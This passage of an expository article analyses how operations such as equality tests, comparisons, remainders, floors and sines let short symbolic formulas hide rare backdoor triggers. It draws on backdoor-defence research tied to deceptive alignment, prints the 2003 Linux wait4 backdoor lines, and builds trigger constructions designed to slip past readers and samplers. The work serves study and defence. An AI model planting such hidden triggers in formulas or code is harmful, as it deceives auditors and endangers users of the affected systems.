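# Which Operations Let a Short Formula or Program Hide a Rare Trigger

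## Symbolic models, grammars and hidden triggers

A symbolic model is a formula or short program that maps inputs to outputs. A person or machine writes it in a grammar, which specifies the permitted operations (such as addition or "is x greater than y"), the available constants, and the rules for combining them. Symbolic models attract interest as a readable alternative to neural networks. A formula of twenty symbols fits on one line, while a neural network's behaviour depends on millions or billions of numerical weights that nobody can check by eye.

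Even a formula that fits on one line can follow a simple rule on billions of inputs and break it on one. Security researchers call a planted exception like this a backdoor, and the input that sets it off a trigger. Whether a short formula can contain a backdoor depends largely on the operations in its grammar. If the grammar has only addition, constants and the variable x, every formula is a straight line. Two straight lines that agree at two points agree everywhere, so a lone exception is impossible. If the grammar also includes an equality test, an exception takes four extra symbols.

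### Where the formulas come from

*Interpretable Machine Learning for Science with PySR and SymbolicRegression.jl* (Cranmer, 2023) describes symbolic regression as a type of machine learning that aims at symbolic models people can interpret. The user supplies a table of inputs and responses and a list of operations, and the software looks for a short formula, built from those operations, that comes close to the responses. Ordinary regression fixes the form of the formula in advance (a straight line, say) and adjusts only the numbers, whereas symbolic regression also searches over forms, which takes a lot of computation. *Decision-Making under Combinatorial Risk* (2026) notes that the problem is NP-hard, meaning that no known method solves every instance quickly, and that the number of candidate formulas grows exponentially with the depth of the formula.

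Most tools get around this with genetic programming, a search that imitates breeding. They keep a population of formulas, each a tree with operations at the branching points and variables or constants at the leaves. They score every formula by its error on the data, drop those that score poorly, and make new ones by swapping an operation, slightly changing a constant, or exchanging branches between two trees.

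The data can also come from another model. Morales and Sheppard (2025), in *Decomposable Neuro Symbolic Regression*, first train an opaque regression model, then vary one input at a time while holding the others fixed, and distil the responses into a formula that explains what the model computes. An auditor who wants to replace weights with something readable would rely on this step. However, Morales and Sheppard point out that the search space contains many formulas that are written differently but compute nearly the same function within the studied domain. The score does not measure whether these formulas also agree outside that domain or between the data points.

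Program synthesis starts from a specification. *From Provable Correctness to Probabilistic Generation* (2025) describes the syntax-guided form, in which the user supplies a logical condition that the unknown function must satisfy for every input and a grammar that generates all the allowed expressions. Suppose the condition is that f(x, y) is at least x, at least y, and equal to one of them. If the grammar has comparison and if-then-else, "if x ≤ y then y else x" is a solution. As *Modelling Program Spaces in Program Synthesis with Constraints* (2025) describes, the search typically begins with an empty program and applies the grammar's rules to fill its holes until none remain.

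*Can LLMs Perform Synthesis?* (2026) tested the solver cvc5 and several language models on such problems, checking every answer for both conformity to the grammar and correctness. The correctness check uses a condition that covers every input, such as "for all x, f(x) = 3x + 2", so it rules out a trigger anywhere. A specification can also consist of examples, but ten thousand examples of 3x + 2 rule out a trigger only at those ten thousand inputs.

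### One tool's menu

Cranmer, Ashok and colleagues (2026), in *MilesCranmer/PySR*, released version 2.0.0a2 of PySR, an open-source library for symbolic regression, in May 2026. The documentation page PySR's *Operators* lists several dozen ready-made operations, among them these:

| Kind | Operators | Behaviour |
|---|---|---|
| Arithmetic | +, −, *, /, ^, abs, square | as in school algebra |
| Smooth and periodic | exp, log, tanh, sin, cos | as on a scientific calculator |
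| Remainder and rounding | mod, round, floor, ceil | mod gives the remainder after division |
| Comparison | >, >=, <, <= | 1 if true, 0 if false |
| Choice | max, min, clamp, cond | cond(x, y) gives y if x is positive, otherwise 0 |
| Logic | logical_and, logical_or | 1 or 0, treating positive numbers as true |

The list has no equality test, but this matters little because, according to the same page, almost any function of one or two numbers written in the programming language Julia will work as a custom operator.

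PySR's default grammar is much more limited. Its *API Reference* lists +, −, * and / as the default operations and 30 as the default limit on a formula's size. A PySR model can contain remainders, rounding or comparisons only if the user adds them. Users can also restrict nesting, for instance by forbidding a cosine inside a sine. The documentation recommends using few operators because extra ones can exponentially enlarge the search; it does not discuss backdoors.

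### A running example, and the vocabulary

Let x be a 32-bit input, a whole number from 0 to 4,294,967,295. The ordinary output is 3x + 2. At one input, a, the output must differ. Arithmetic is exact, with no rounding. If the grammar has an equality test that gives 1 when true and 0 when false, one formula that does the job is

3·x + 2 + (x = a)

The *trigger* is the input, or small set of inputs, on which the model departs from its ordinary behaviour. In this example, it is the single input a. Replacing the equality test with (x > 4,294,967,290) would make the trigger a set of five inputs.

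*Rarity*, written ε, is the share of inputs on which the departure occurs, under a stated distribution. Suppose a formula departs only when x = a. If x is equally likely to be any 32-bit value, ε is 1/2³², or about 2.3 × 10⁻¹⁰. If x is a person's age and a is 42, the formula departs on one or two inputs in a hundred.

*Expression size* is the total number of occurrences of operations, variables and constants. The formula 3·x + 2 has size 5, and size 9 with the trigger. PySR's *Features and Options* describes the same default measure, so the formula with the trigger is well within the limit of 30.

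*Constant bits* are the binary digits needed to write a formula's constants, which are not counted in expression size. The trigger's constant takes 4 bits when a = 10 and 32 bits when a = 2,718,281,828, but both formulas have size 9. The printed formula may not show the exact constant either. PySR prints numbers to five significant digits by default, so a hundred thousand different whole numbers are all printed as 2.7183 × 10⁹.

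The *closure* of a grammar is the set of all functions that can be built by combining its primitives, the operations it supplies directly. A grammar with max and negation but no absolute value still has absolute value in its closure, because max(x, −x) computes it. Two comparisons can likewise be combined into an equality test, so an audit that checks only the list of primitives can miss operations that the grammar is able to express.

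The *VC dimension* (after Vapnik and Chervonenkis) of a family of yes-or-no functions measures its flexibility. It is the size of the largest set of inputs on which the family can produce every pattern of yes and no. The tests "x = a", one for each value of a, have VC dimension 1 because they can give either answer at any single point, but none can give yes at two. Tests of the form "x = a or x = b" have VC dimension 2.

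### Why random testing misses the trigger

A sampling test runs the model on random inputs and looks for odd outputs. With m independent draws, the chance of at least one hit is 1 − (1 − ε)^m, which is close to mε when mε is small. For a million draws in the running example, it is about 1,000,000 / 4,294,967,296, or 0.00023. A tester needs 1/ε draws on average to get a first hit, which is about 4.3 billion here, and about three times as many for a 95% chance of at least one hit.

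If a million draws produce no odd output, the same arithmetic gives 95% confidence that ε is below roughly 3 in a million. That bound still allows nearly 13,000 trigger inputs.

*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) gives the practical example of a bank that outsources the training of a loan classifier and checks the result on held-out customer data. This check measures average accuracy well but misses misbehaviour on specific inputs that are rare in the data, including inputs the contractor deliberately prepared.

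The running example's 32-bit input is small enough to test exhaustively. At a billion evaluations a second, trying every value takes a little over four seconds, but with two 32-bit inputs the same machine would need about 585 years. A trigger's rarity depends on how many inputs set it off, and that number is easy to get wrong. *Automated Whitebox Fuzz Testing*, by Godefroid, Levin and Molnar, discusses a program that compares its four input bytes with the characters of "bad!" and crashes on three or more matches. The paper gives the number of crashing inputs as 5 out of 2³², a chance of about 1 in 2³⁰, but five is the number of crashing paths through the program. Each three-match path admits 255 values for the byte that fails to match, so 1,021 inputs crash the program, or about 1 in 4.2 million. A million random draws would find one roughly a fifth of the time.

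### Samplers, readers and solvers

Sampling uses only the model's inputs and outputs. Someone who has the formula can read it and see the exception directly, as in 3·x + 2 + (x = a). They can also give the formula to a solver, a program that searches for an input satisfying a logical or arithmetic condition or proves that none exists.

*DART* (Godefroid, Klarlund and Sen, 2005), a paper on automated software testing, shows how large the difference is. Its example program crashes if x and y differ and 2x equals x + 10. The tool first runs the program on random values, x = 269,167,349 and y = 889,801,541, which don't cause a crash. It records, in symbolic form, each condition the program tests, then reverses the last one and uses a solver to find an x with 2x = x + 10. The solution is x = 10, and the second run crashes. A random 32-bit x would have had one chance in 2³² of causing the crash.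 *A Survey of Symbolic Execution Techniques* (2016) attributes the advantage to reasoning about whole classes of inputs at once, whereas a sampler tries one value at a time.

A solver's limits depend on the operations in the program. When a program multiplies two quantities that both depend on the input, DART can't apply its linear reasoning and uses the concrete number from the current run instead. The number of paths also grows rapidly with program size. A short formula usually has few enough paths to avoid this second problem, but it can easily include such a multiplication.

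A suspect operation raises three questions: whether the grammar can express the trigger, directly or by combining its operations; how long the expression is, in size and in constant bits; and whether a sampler, a reader or a solver can find the trigger. An equality test can express the trigger with four extra symbols and a constant of at most 32 bits. A sampler fails to find it, but a reader and a solver each find it immediately. Other operations give less favorable combinations of answers.

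### The attacker and defender game

Goldwasser and colleagues proved, under cryptographic assumptions, that a dishonest trainer can plant a backdoor in certain classifiers and that no efficient examiner can detect it, even with the model's full description. Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, therefore give the defender the easier task of deciding, at the moment of use, whether a particular input is the trigger. They define this task as a game over a class F of functions with outputs 0 and 1, which runs as follows.

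1. The attacker, who knows the defender's method, picks a distribution D over inputs and an original function f from F.
2. A random draw from D fixes the trigger x*.
3. The attacker sees x* and picks a backdoored function f* from F. It must differ from f at x*, and may differ from f on at most a share ε of inputs under D.
4. A fair coin decides whether the defender receives f with a fresh random input, or f* with x*. The defender has the full description of the function, can draw further random examples of its behaviour, and must accept or reject.

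The defender wins by accepting the clean pair or rejecting the backdoored one, and also wins if the attacker's f* broke the conditions in step 3. F is ε-defendable with confidence 1 − δ if some method wins with probability at least 1 − δ against every attacker. For example, if the original is 3·x + 2 and the backdoored version is 3·x + 2 + (x = a), the defender only has to read the constant a, compare it with the input, and reject if they match.

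The random draw in step 2 is there because the game is hopeless without it. If attackers could pick the trigger, ARC's *Backdoors as an analogy for deceptive alignment* explains, they would take two functions that agree on most inputs and use a point of disagreement, and in general the defender could do no better than guess. (ARC is the Alignment Research Center, where the game originated.)

The timing of the draw matters too. If the attacker learns the trigger a before choosing the original function, they can offer 3·x + 2 + (x = a) as the original and 3·x + 2 + (x = b), with b random, as the backdoored version. In either case, the defender receives a formula with a special case at one random point, together with an unrelated random input. The two cases look identical, so no method wins more than half the time. The attacker has removed an existing backdoor instead of inserting one. Christiano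 and colleagues analyze this for the bare tests "x = a" and remark that it would be an extreme failure for the defender, given that the class has a VC dimension of only 1.

A suggested variant for numerical outputs such as 3x + 2 requires the average squared difference between f and f* to be at most ε and the gap at the trigger to be at least 1. It penalises large departures as well as frequent ones. At a single 32-bit input, a gap of 1 contributes 2⁻³² to the average, while a gap of 65,536 contributes 1.

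Under the original rules, Christiano and colleagues prove that VC dimension essentially determines whether a defender with unlimited computing time can win. They also prove that decision trees of moderate size can be defended efficiently when inputs are uniformly distributed, and that, under cryptographic assumptions, general circuits of moderate size cannot. These results apply only partly to an audit, because someone who plants a backdoor in a formula will usually choose the trigger to suit a purpose, and an auditor wants to know whether any trigger exists before a suspicious input turns up.

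The attacker's access to the model also matters. In the game, the attacker writes f* directly. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considers an attacker who can only corrupt the labels in the training data, and proves that this method cannot produce a backdoor with cryptographic protection. A training procedure that installs the trigger rule from labelled examples also learns the rule, so a defender with as many labelled examples can run the same procedure. By that reasoning, a finished formula from an untrusted author deserves more suspicion than one that a trusted tool has fitted to possibly corrupted labels. But Kaneko's defender needs representative, correctly labelled examples of the trigger, and an auditor looking for a single unknown a has none.

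## Exact equality tests and chains of comparisons

In the running example, 3·x + 2 + (x = a), the exception takes four symbols, and a few more can make it larger or rarer. Multiplying the test by a constant, as in 3·x + 2 + 1000·(x = a), adds two symbols and sets how far the output departs from 3·x + 2 when x = a. If the model has a second 32-bit input y, replacing (x = a) with (x = a)·(y = b) adds four symbols, including the constant b, and reduces ε from 1/2³² to 1/2⁶⁴. PySR's default limit of 30 symbols leaves room for six such tests beside 3·x + 2, so a formula with six 32-bit inputs could contain a trigger with ε = 1/2¹⁹².

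Most of the information in an equality test is in its constant, since specifying an arbitrary one of 2³² values takes 32 bits. An attacker who doesn't mind which input becomes the trigger can use a shorter test. The test (x = 0) needs only a one-bit constant. The test (x = y) needs no constant, and is true only once in 2³² draws on average when x and y are independent, uniformly random 32-bit inputs.

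### Equality without the equals sign

A grammar designer might strike "=" from the list and keep the order comparisons, which are useful for thresholds. This changes very little. The conditions x ≥ a and x ≤ a hold together only at x = a, so 3·x + 2 + (x ≥ a)·(x ≤ a) is the same function as before, at size 13 instead of 9. A single strict comparison operator is enough:

3·x + 3 − (x > a) − (a > x)

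For any x other than a, exactly one of the comparisons gives 1, and the output is 3x + 2. At x = a, both give 0, and the output is 3a + 3. This formula also has size 13, and it doesn't multiply two comparisons.

Both versions contain the constant a twice, and an auditor might look for that repetition. On whole numbers, (x > a − 1)·(x < a + 1) also tests whether x equals a, but uses two different constants. If a is 2,718,281,828 and the software prints five significant digits, as PySR does by default, both constants appear as 2.7183 × 10⁹. The printed condition then looks impossible to meet, and a reader could easily dismiss it as a leftover from the search.

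At either end of the input range, a single order comparison can test for equality, because x ≥ 4,294,967,295 holds for exactly one unsigned 32-bit value. To prevent equality tests, a designer would have to remove order comparisons as well as the equality operator, and even then such tests can be built from absolute values or powers.

The arithmetic is different when the inputs are separate yes-or-no features. *Queries and Concept Learning* (Angluin, 1988) describes formulas that join n conditions with "and", where condition i is either "bit i is on" or "bit i is off". Exactly one setting of the n bits satisfies each such formula. A chain of d tests on separate bits therefore isolates 1 input in 2^d, and the pattern of negations, rather than a numerical constant, determines which inputs match. For 32 bits and a typical target, the chain needs about 79 symbols, made up of 32 variables, 31 "and"s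 and about 16 negations.

When each variable is a single bit, a size limit restricts how rare a condition can be. A condition that reads d bits holds on a whole-number multiple of 1/2^d of uniformly random inputs. A formula of at most 30 symbols, built from operations that take one or two arguments, has room for at most 15 variables, so any condition in it that can hold does so at least 1 time in 32,768. A comparison on a 32-bit number replaces a 32-step chain with three symbols, so the size limit no longer rules out much rarer conditions.

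### Searching from outside

Angluin also proved a worst-case bound for a searcher who sees only answers. Suppose the searcher knows that exactly one n-bit string is special and may ask of any string whether it is the special one. An adversary starts with a list of all 2^n strings, answers "no" each time, and crosses off the string the searcher asked about. The answers so far fit every string still on the list, so the searcher can't identify the special one while two or more remain. Each question removes at most one string, so the searcher can need 2^n − 1 questions.

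Finding the string a that passes an equality test on a 32-bit input takes 4,294,967,295 evaluations in the worst case, and about half as many on average if a is random and the searcher never repeats an input. Choosing inputs based on earlier answers doesn't help, because each "no" rules out only the string just tried.

The bound applies to exact identification. Angluin shows that the number of random examples needed grows only in proportion to n if the searcher accepts a guess that is probably right on all but a small share of inputs. The searcher names the special string if it appears in the sample, and otherwise names any string that did not appear. The second answer is usually wrong about which string is special, but it still counts as a success because the error affects so few inputs. An auditor can therefore learn nothing about a trigger from a valid certificate that a model is "approximately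 correct".

The search ends at once if the searcher can propose a set, ask whether it contains the special string, and receive that string in reply when it does not. Running the model, however many times, does not supply this reply. A solver with access to the formula can, because "find an x where the output differs from 3x + 2" reduces to x = a.

### Reading the text: the Linux case of 2003

A person with the formula in hand doesn't need queries either, since the constant is in plain sight. They still have to notice what it does. In November 2003 someone added two lines to a copy of the source code of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system. The lines went into wait4, a function that programs call to wait for something to happen:

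```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The variable options is a 32-bit word whose bits switch features on, and the first test is true only when two particular bits are on and the rest are off. In C, "==" compares and "=" assigns, and the part after "&&" runs only if the part before it is true. So a program that called wait4 with that combination got user ID 0, which belongs to the administrator and allows any action on the machine. The assignment has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the second line never ran and this check produced no error. An intruder who knew the combination would need only one call, but a uniformly random value of options would match about once in 4.3 billion calls.

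McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, reported that a routine check of the copied files had flagged one whose three newest entries lacked the pointer that tied every legitimate change to the master record. The oldest of the three, from the day before, had added two lines. *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, from Princeton's Center for Information Technology Policy, points out that an expert reading casually would take these lines for harmless error checking. Neither a test nor a code review detected them.

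McVoy posted the lines to the kernel mailing list at 17:26 in a follow-up, *Re: BK2CVS problem* (2003). Within 22 minutes another subscriber, Chad Kitching, suggested that they were an attempted backdoor. McVoy agreed and admitted that he had missed the single equals sign. A reply the next day, *Re: BK2CVS problem* (2003), explained that the altered copy could not have reached a kernel release, because changes entered either as emailed patches or through merges in the master system, and the people who merged there didn't use the copy.

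This is decent evidence that readers can spot a planted equality test, but only once something has directed them to the right two lines. A reader of a twenty-symbol formula is in roughly that position from the start. The disguise also depended on an assignment inside a condition, which a grammar of pure formulas does not allow. However, McVoy misread the lines even though he knew the code was suspect.

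### Recovering the constant with a solver

The program from Godefroid and colleagues that reads four bytes and crashes when at least three match "bad!" has only 16 possible paths. Starting from the input "good", a depth-first search that uses a solver to reverse one recorded comparison at a time reaches the first crash on its eighth run.

Brumley, Hartwig and colleagues, in *Automatically Identifying Trigger-based Behavior in Malware*, applied the same idea to malicious programs without using their source code. Their example is a worm that attacks when four comparisons all succeed: day 9, hour 10, month 11, minute 6. A tester who fills the four 16-bit fields with random bits has a 1 in 2⁶⁴ chance of matching all four, while one who picks a random minute of a 365-day year has a 1 in 525,600 chance.

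Their tool, MineSweeper, runs the program in an emulator and treats chosen inputs, such as the clock or network messages, as unknowns. Everything that doesn't depend on those inputs runs normally. At each branch that does depend on them, the tool uses a solver to find values for either direction, much as DART does, and runs the program again with those values. Brumley and colleagues tried it on four real programs:

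| Program | What MineSweeper recovered | Branches on trigger inputs | Total time | Time in the solver |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| NetSky, an email worm | attack time: 26 February 2004, 6 to 9 am | 6 | 9 min | 0.3 min |
| MyDoom, an email worm | attack dates of 1 and 3 February 2004, stop date of 12 February | 11 | 28 min | 2.2 min |
| Perfect Keylogger | the window-title text that switches on recording | 2 | 2 min | under 0.1 min |
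| TFN, a network attack tool | the command values it obeys | 14 | 21 min | 6.5 min |

Running the programs took most of the time, and solving the comparisons took only a small part of it. The keylogger was harder to analyze because it compared the window title with its key one byte at a time. The tool was slow to work through the resulting branches until the researchers gave it a summary of what the text-search function computes. Brumley and colleagues confirmed that the tool found all the trigger behaviour already known in these programs, but they did not show that it would find everything in an unfamiliar one. They also note that a program can defeat the tool by hashing the input before testing it.

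Dantas, Cordeiro and Junior (2026), in *Detecting Ladder Logic Bombs in IEC 61131-3 PLC Programs using ESBMC-PLC+*, tested a verifier that looks for sabotage code in the programs that run industrial controllers. It detected all 30 programs in a public set of malicious programs, whose triggers are equality and order comparisons, and recovered every trigger. On 310 generated programs with yes-or-no and whole-number logic, it missed nothing and raised no false alarms, with a median time of 70 milliseconds. It also caught triggers that the team had rewritten, for instance with roundabout arithmetic, to evade a tool that inspects program structure. When a program contains no violation, the verifier can often prove this for every possible run.

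The proof covers only what the user has specified. Dantas and colleagues detect a payload if it stops the program from finishing or violates a stated safety condition, and they place everything else out of scope. An auditor of a symbolic model has the same problem. If the auditor has a trusted reference formula, such as 3x + 2, a solver can search for inputs where the model disagrees with it. Otherwise, the solver can still list the inputs that make each comparison true, but the auditor has to judge which of these exceptions are legitimate.

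Solvers do get stuck, usually because of the arithmetic that comes before the comparison. In the same study, the detection rate fell from 99% to 49% on a later set of controller programs, which included loops that repeatedly square a number, as the solver ran out of time. *Defusing Logic Bombs in Symbolic Execution with LLM-Generated Ghost Code* (Bouras and Mechtaev, 2026) discusses a branch in a mathematical library that requires sin(x)·cos(x) to be negative. A standard tool fails on it. The paper's tool has a language model write a routine that recovers x from its sine and cosine, lets the solver handle the remaining conditions, and finds x = 2. The sign condition holds for about half of all angles, so a sampler would meet it almost immediately. A condition can therefore be hard for a solver without being rare, while a plain equality test is rarely met but easy to solve.

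Language models also help with the harder cases. *Symbolon* (2026) describes a system that uses one to rewrite troublesome code before analysis. On a benchmark of 53 small programs designed to defeat symbolic execution tools, the system covered all the code in 50, compared with 12 for ordinary symbolic execution.

### Checking one input in a decision tree

A decision tree is a set of chains of comparisons that share their early steps. Each internal node tests one input bit and sends the input left or right, and each leaf holds an output of 0 or 1. Christiano and colleagues found a defence for their attacker-and-defender game that applies to trees of moderate size with uniformly random inputs and takes no longer than evaluating the tree once. The defender follows the input to its leaf, counts the distinct bits tested on that path, and rejects the input if the count is too high.

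Suppose a tree on 32 bits outputs the top bit, using two leaves at depth 1. To change the output on input a alone, the attacker has to test the other 31 bits too, which puts a at depth 32 in a tree of 33 leaves. By the general argument, any other arrangement also has a deep leaf. Let s be the maximum number of leaves and δ the tolerated chance of failure. The defender rejects when 1/2^depth is at most δ/s. With s = 500 and δ = 1%, the defender rejects at depth 16 or more.

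1. A uniformly random input reaches a given leaf at depth k with probability 1/2^k. Leaves at depth 16 or more each receive at most 0.00002 of the inputs, and there are at most 500 of them, so the defender wrongly rejects a clean pair at most 1% of the time.
2. The trigger is itself a random draw. By the same count, the original tree f sends it to a leaf at depth 15 or less with probability at least 99%.
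3. Now take all inputs that share the trigger's leaf in f and also share its leaf in the backdoored tree f*. Each tree has one output per leaf, and the two disagree at the trigger, so they disagree on this whole set.
4. Membership in that set fixes at most depth(f) + depth(f*) bits. The set therefore makes up at least 1/2^(depth(f) + depth(f*)) of all inputs, and the rules limit it to ε.
5. If ε is 1/2³², the two depths add up to at least 32. The original tree accounts for at most 15, which leaves at least 17 for f*, and the defender rejects.

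The proof needs ε below δ²/s². Here that is 4 × 10⁻¹⁰, and 1/2³² is about 2.3 × 10⁻¹⁰.

Step 4 works when the input bits are uniform, and Christiano and colleagues note that the bits must at least be independent. Suppose instead that the first two bits of real inputs differ only once in 2³² cases. If the original tree outputs the first bit and the altered tree outputs the second, the trees differ only on those rare inputs, even though every leaf in both has depth 1. This trick would seldom win the game, because the trigger there is random and its first two bits nearly always match. But an attacker who chooses the trigger can pick one whose first two bits differ. Christiano and colleagues suspect that similar checks exist for other functions made of constant pieces, perhaps even without uniform inputs, but they don't prove it.

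The check can also fail when the original tree already contains the special case. If f has a leaf at depth 32 for a, and the attacker deletes it, a reaches a shallow leaf in the altered tree and the defender accepts. Step 4 guarantees only that the two depths have a large sum, and here the large depth is in the original tree. The proof still holds because a random trigger rarely lands on a deep leaf of f, but again this does not help if the attacker chose a. The defender also rejects a legitimate exception, such as a reserved error code, every time it comes up.

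An auditor can inspect a tree before it is used, without waiting for an input. A tree with 500 leaves has at most 500 regions, so the auditor can list the deep ones and ask for a reason for each.

Formulas are harder to treat this way, because they can compute a rare chain without displaying it. A natural analogue of the depth check would look at the values entering each "and" and "or" and flag combinations that random inputs seldom produce. Christiano and colleagues give a counterexample found by Thomas Read. With four bits, and with adjacent terms meaning "and", it compares

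x₄x₃ with ((x₁ or x₄x₂)x₂ or x₄x₃)x₃

Multiplying out the second formula gives x₁x₂x₃ or x₄x₃, so the two formulas differ only when the first three bits are on and the fourth is off. The same pattern on n bits gives formulas that differ on one input in 2^n. However long the disguised formula gets, each of its operations receives each possible combination of values on at least an eighth of random inputs. The chain x₁x₂x₃ appears only when the brackets are expanded, and Christiano and colleagues suggest that a defence for formulas might start by rewriting them.

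## Remainders, floors and periodic functions

An author who wants (x = a) to fire at an arbitrary 32-bit input has to write down a 32-bit constant, which an auditor can look for. Remainders can make a trigger rare without such a large constant. A whole number divisible by 3, 5, 7, 11, 13, 17, 19 and 23 is also divisible by their product, 111,546,435. Eight conditions that each hold fairly often therefore select one in every 111,546,435 whole numbers, with no constant above 23.

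Combining them doesn't take an equality test or a comparison. Let s be the sum of the eight remainders:

s = x mod 3 + x mod 5 + x mod 7 + x mod 11 + x mod 13 + x mod 17 + x mod 19 + x mod 23

Remainders are never negative, so s is 0 only when all eight are 0. Otherwise it lies between 1 and 90. One more remainder turns this into an exception:

3·x + 1 + (1 mod (1 + s))

When s is 0, the last term is the remainder when 1 is divided by 1, which is 0. For any larger s, the last term is 1. The output is therefore 3x + 2 everywhere except at multiples of 111,546,435, where it is 3x + 1. The 32-bit range has 39 such multiples, counting 0, so ε is about 9 × 10⁻⁹. A million random draws would have about a 0.9% chance of hitting one.

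This formula has size 41, which is over PySR's default limit of 30. Five remainders fit within the limit, and the divisors don't have to be prime as long as no two share a factor. With the divisors 25, 27, 28, 29 and 31, a formula of size 29 differs from 3x + 2 on one input in 16,991,100.

Zero is a poor trigger because it is one of the first inputs a tester tries. The author can move the trigger to any other whole number by adding a small shift inside each remainder. For instance, (x + 1) mod 3 is 0 when x leaves remainder 2 on division by 3. If no two divisors share a factor greater than 1, the Chinese remainder theorem shows that every combination of remainders occurs exactly once in each run of consecutive whole numbers whose length is the product of the divisors.

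The earlier example, a = 2,718,281,828, leaves remainders 0, 2, 3, 3, 9, 2, 1, 12, 10 and 4 when divided by the ten primes from 2 to 29. The product of these primes is 6,469,693,230, which is more than 2³², so no other 32-bit number leaves the same ten remainders. With the matching shifts, the formula differs from 3x + 2 only at a, just as it would with (x = a), but no constant in it exceeds 29. It needs 67 symbols instead of 9, and about twice as many bits for its constants. A reader who skims the sum might take it for a checksum, but one who works out what it does can recover a by a routine calculation.

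Floors do the same job. The remainder x mod y is x − y·⌊x/y⌋, where ⌊ ⌋ means rounding down, so a grammar with floor, division, multiplication and subtraction has remainders in its closure. (*Tag-system computation using only powers and principal logarithms* (2026) gets remainders even from powers and logarithms.) Floor also gives a more direct trigger:

3·x + 2 + ⌊x/a⌋ − ⌊(x − 1)/a⌋

The two floors differ by 1 when x is a multiple of a, and are otherwise equal. The only 32-bit multiples of 2,718,281,828 are 0 and the number itself, so this formula of size 17 has two triggers.

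### Combs on the real line

On real numbers, sine can replace the remainder. The function sin(πx/3) is 0 exactly at the multiples of 3, and in general the zeros of sin(ωx) are π/ω apart. Let S be the sum of sin²(πx/p) over the eight primes p from 3 to 23. Squares are never negative, so S is 0 only where all eight terms are 0, which happens at the multiples of the primes' product, 111,546,435.

Adding S to 3x + 2 would change almost every output, because S is positive nearly everywhere, so the author needs a second operation that gives zero away from the trigger. At any whole number that is not a multiple of 111,546,435, S is at least sin²(π/23), or about 0.0185. So 100·max(0.01 − S, 0) is 1 at the multiples and 0 at all other whole numbers. On real inputs, it has a bump about 0.14 wide around each multiple, and these bumps cover roughly one part in 770 million of the line.

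Comparing a single sine with a threshold gives a shorter but less rare condition. The test sin(x) > 0.999999 has four symbols and holds for about one whole number in 2,200. Making it ten times rarer takes two more nines, twice as many extra digits as an equality test needs.

### Why one frequency can fit any pattern

The family of tests "sin(ωx) is positive" has one adjustable number, the frequency ω. The tests "x = a" also have one adjustable number, and their VC dimension is 1. For the sine tests it is infinite. The proof is a standard classroom exercise, and LORIA's *Function classes with infinite VC-dimension* gives it in full. It places n points at 2π/10, 2π/100, 2π/1000 and so on, and lets an opponent label each one plus or minus. The frequency is then

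ω = ½ · (1 + the sum of 10^i over every point i labelled minus)

To see that this works, measure the angle ωx at point j in full turns, which comes to ω/10^j.

1. Each minus label at a later point i contributes ½·10^(i−j) turns. That is a whole number of turns, so it does not affect the sine.
2. A minus label at point j itself contributes half a turn.
3. The 1 and the minus labels at earlier points contribute a little more, always above 0 and below 1/18 of a turn.

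A point labelled plus therefore ends up just past a whole number of turns, where sine is positive, and one labelled minus just past a half turn, where sine is negative. With labels minus, plus, minus, ω is ½(1 + 10 + 1000) = 505.5, and the three angles are 50.55, 5.055 and 0.5055 turns. The argument holds for any n, so there is no largest set of points on which the family can produce every pattern. In the game of Christiano and colleagues, this means that even a defender with unlimited computing time cannot defend the family.

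Floors behave the same way. *Sparsity and Out-of-Distribution Generalization* (2026) starts from a fixed square wave that gives 1 when ⌊x⌋ is odd and 0 when it is even. Like any single fixed function, it has VC dimension 0. Multiplying the input by an adjustable weight c makes the dimension infinite, because the binary digits of c can store any list of outputs for the inputs 2^i. The output for 2^i is 1 exactly when ⌊2^i·c⌋ is odd, which happens when the i-th binary digit of c after the point is 1.

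The list has to be stored somewhere, which limits the result in practice. *Structure of universal formulas* (Yarotsky, 2023) shows by a counting argument that p parameters of B bits each can hold at most pB bits of information about the outputs. A 64-bit frequency can therefore produce every pattern on at most 64 points, wherever they are placed. Similarly, *Coresets for Data Discretization and Sine Wave Fitting* (2022) finds that the VC dimension of a sine-fitting problem on n points grows only with the logarithm of nN when the frequency must be a whole number from 1 to N.

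An attacker would rather fit points that someone else has chosen, such as an auditor's test set. Harman, Kulkarni and Narayanan prove in *sin(ωx) Can Approximate Almost Every Finite Set of Samples* that if the inputs are random real numbers between 0 and 1, this is possible in principle with probability 1. For any target values between −1 and 1, some frequency ω brings sin(ωx) as close as desired to those values at the inputs. They use frequencies of the form 2π·2^m. Multiplying x by 2^m moves its binary digits m places to the left, and sine repeats every 2π, so only the digits from place m + 1 onwards matter. The digits of several random numbers eventually contain any chosen finite strings starting at the same place, so some m works for all the inputs at once.

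For ten inputs and five binary digits of accuracy each, 50 digits have to match, which happens at about one position in 2⁵⁰. The frequency would then have around 10¹⁵ binary digits, and the inputs would need to be exact to that many places, so this wouldn't work against a test set of ordinary 64-bit numbers.

Hiding a trigger among whole-number inputs is difficult for a different reason. Yarotsky points out that a single sine wave can't have the signs + + + − + on five equally spaced points, because sin(u − v) + sin(u + v) = 2·sin(u)·cos(v). Centred on the second point, this identity requires cos(v) to be positive, but centred on the fourth it requires cos(v) to be negative. A long run of whole numbers with only one minus sign would contain this pattern or its mirror image, so the sign of one sine wave can't produce it. A family with infinite VC dimension can fit some large sets in every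 possible way, but these may not include the sets an attacker cares about.

Sums of sines inherit restrictions of this kind. Yarotsky shows that the values of any sum of N waves satisfy fixed polynomial equations, whatever the frequencies. Putting one sine inside another generally removes these restrictions. He gives examples of fixed-size nested formulas that can fit any finite set of samples as closely as desired but can't approximate every continuous function on the whole interval. He considers such families especially dangerous because a good fit to the samples is little evidence of a good fit elsewhere. PySR's nesting limits can prevent a sine inside another sine, but only if the user names that combination. For example, a rule against a cosine inside a sine still allows sin(sin(x)).

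He also identifies unbounded inputs as what makes sine a special case. A formula with adjustable parameters, built from arithmetic, exponentials, logarithms and sines, has finite VC dimension if the input to every sine stays within a fixed bounded interval. O-minimal structures exclude unrestricted sine for the same reason. They allow only subsets of the real line made of finitely many points and intervals, and sine has infinitely many isolated zeros.

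### Where a solver always succeeds

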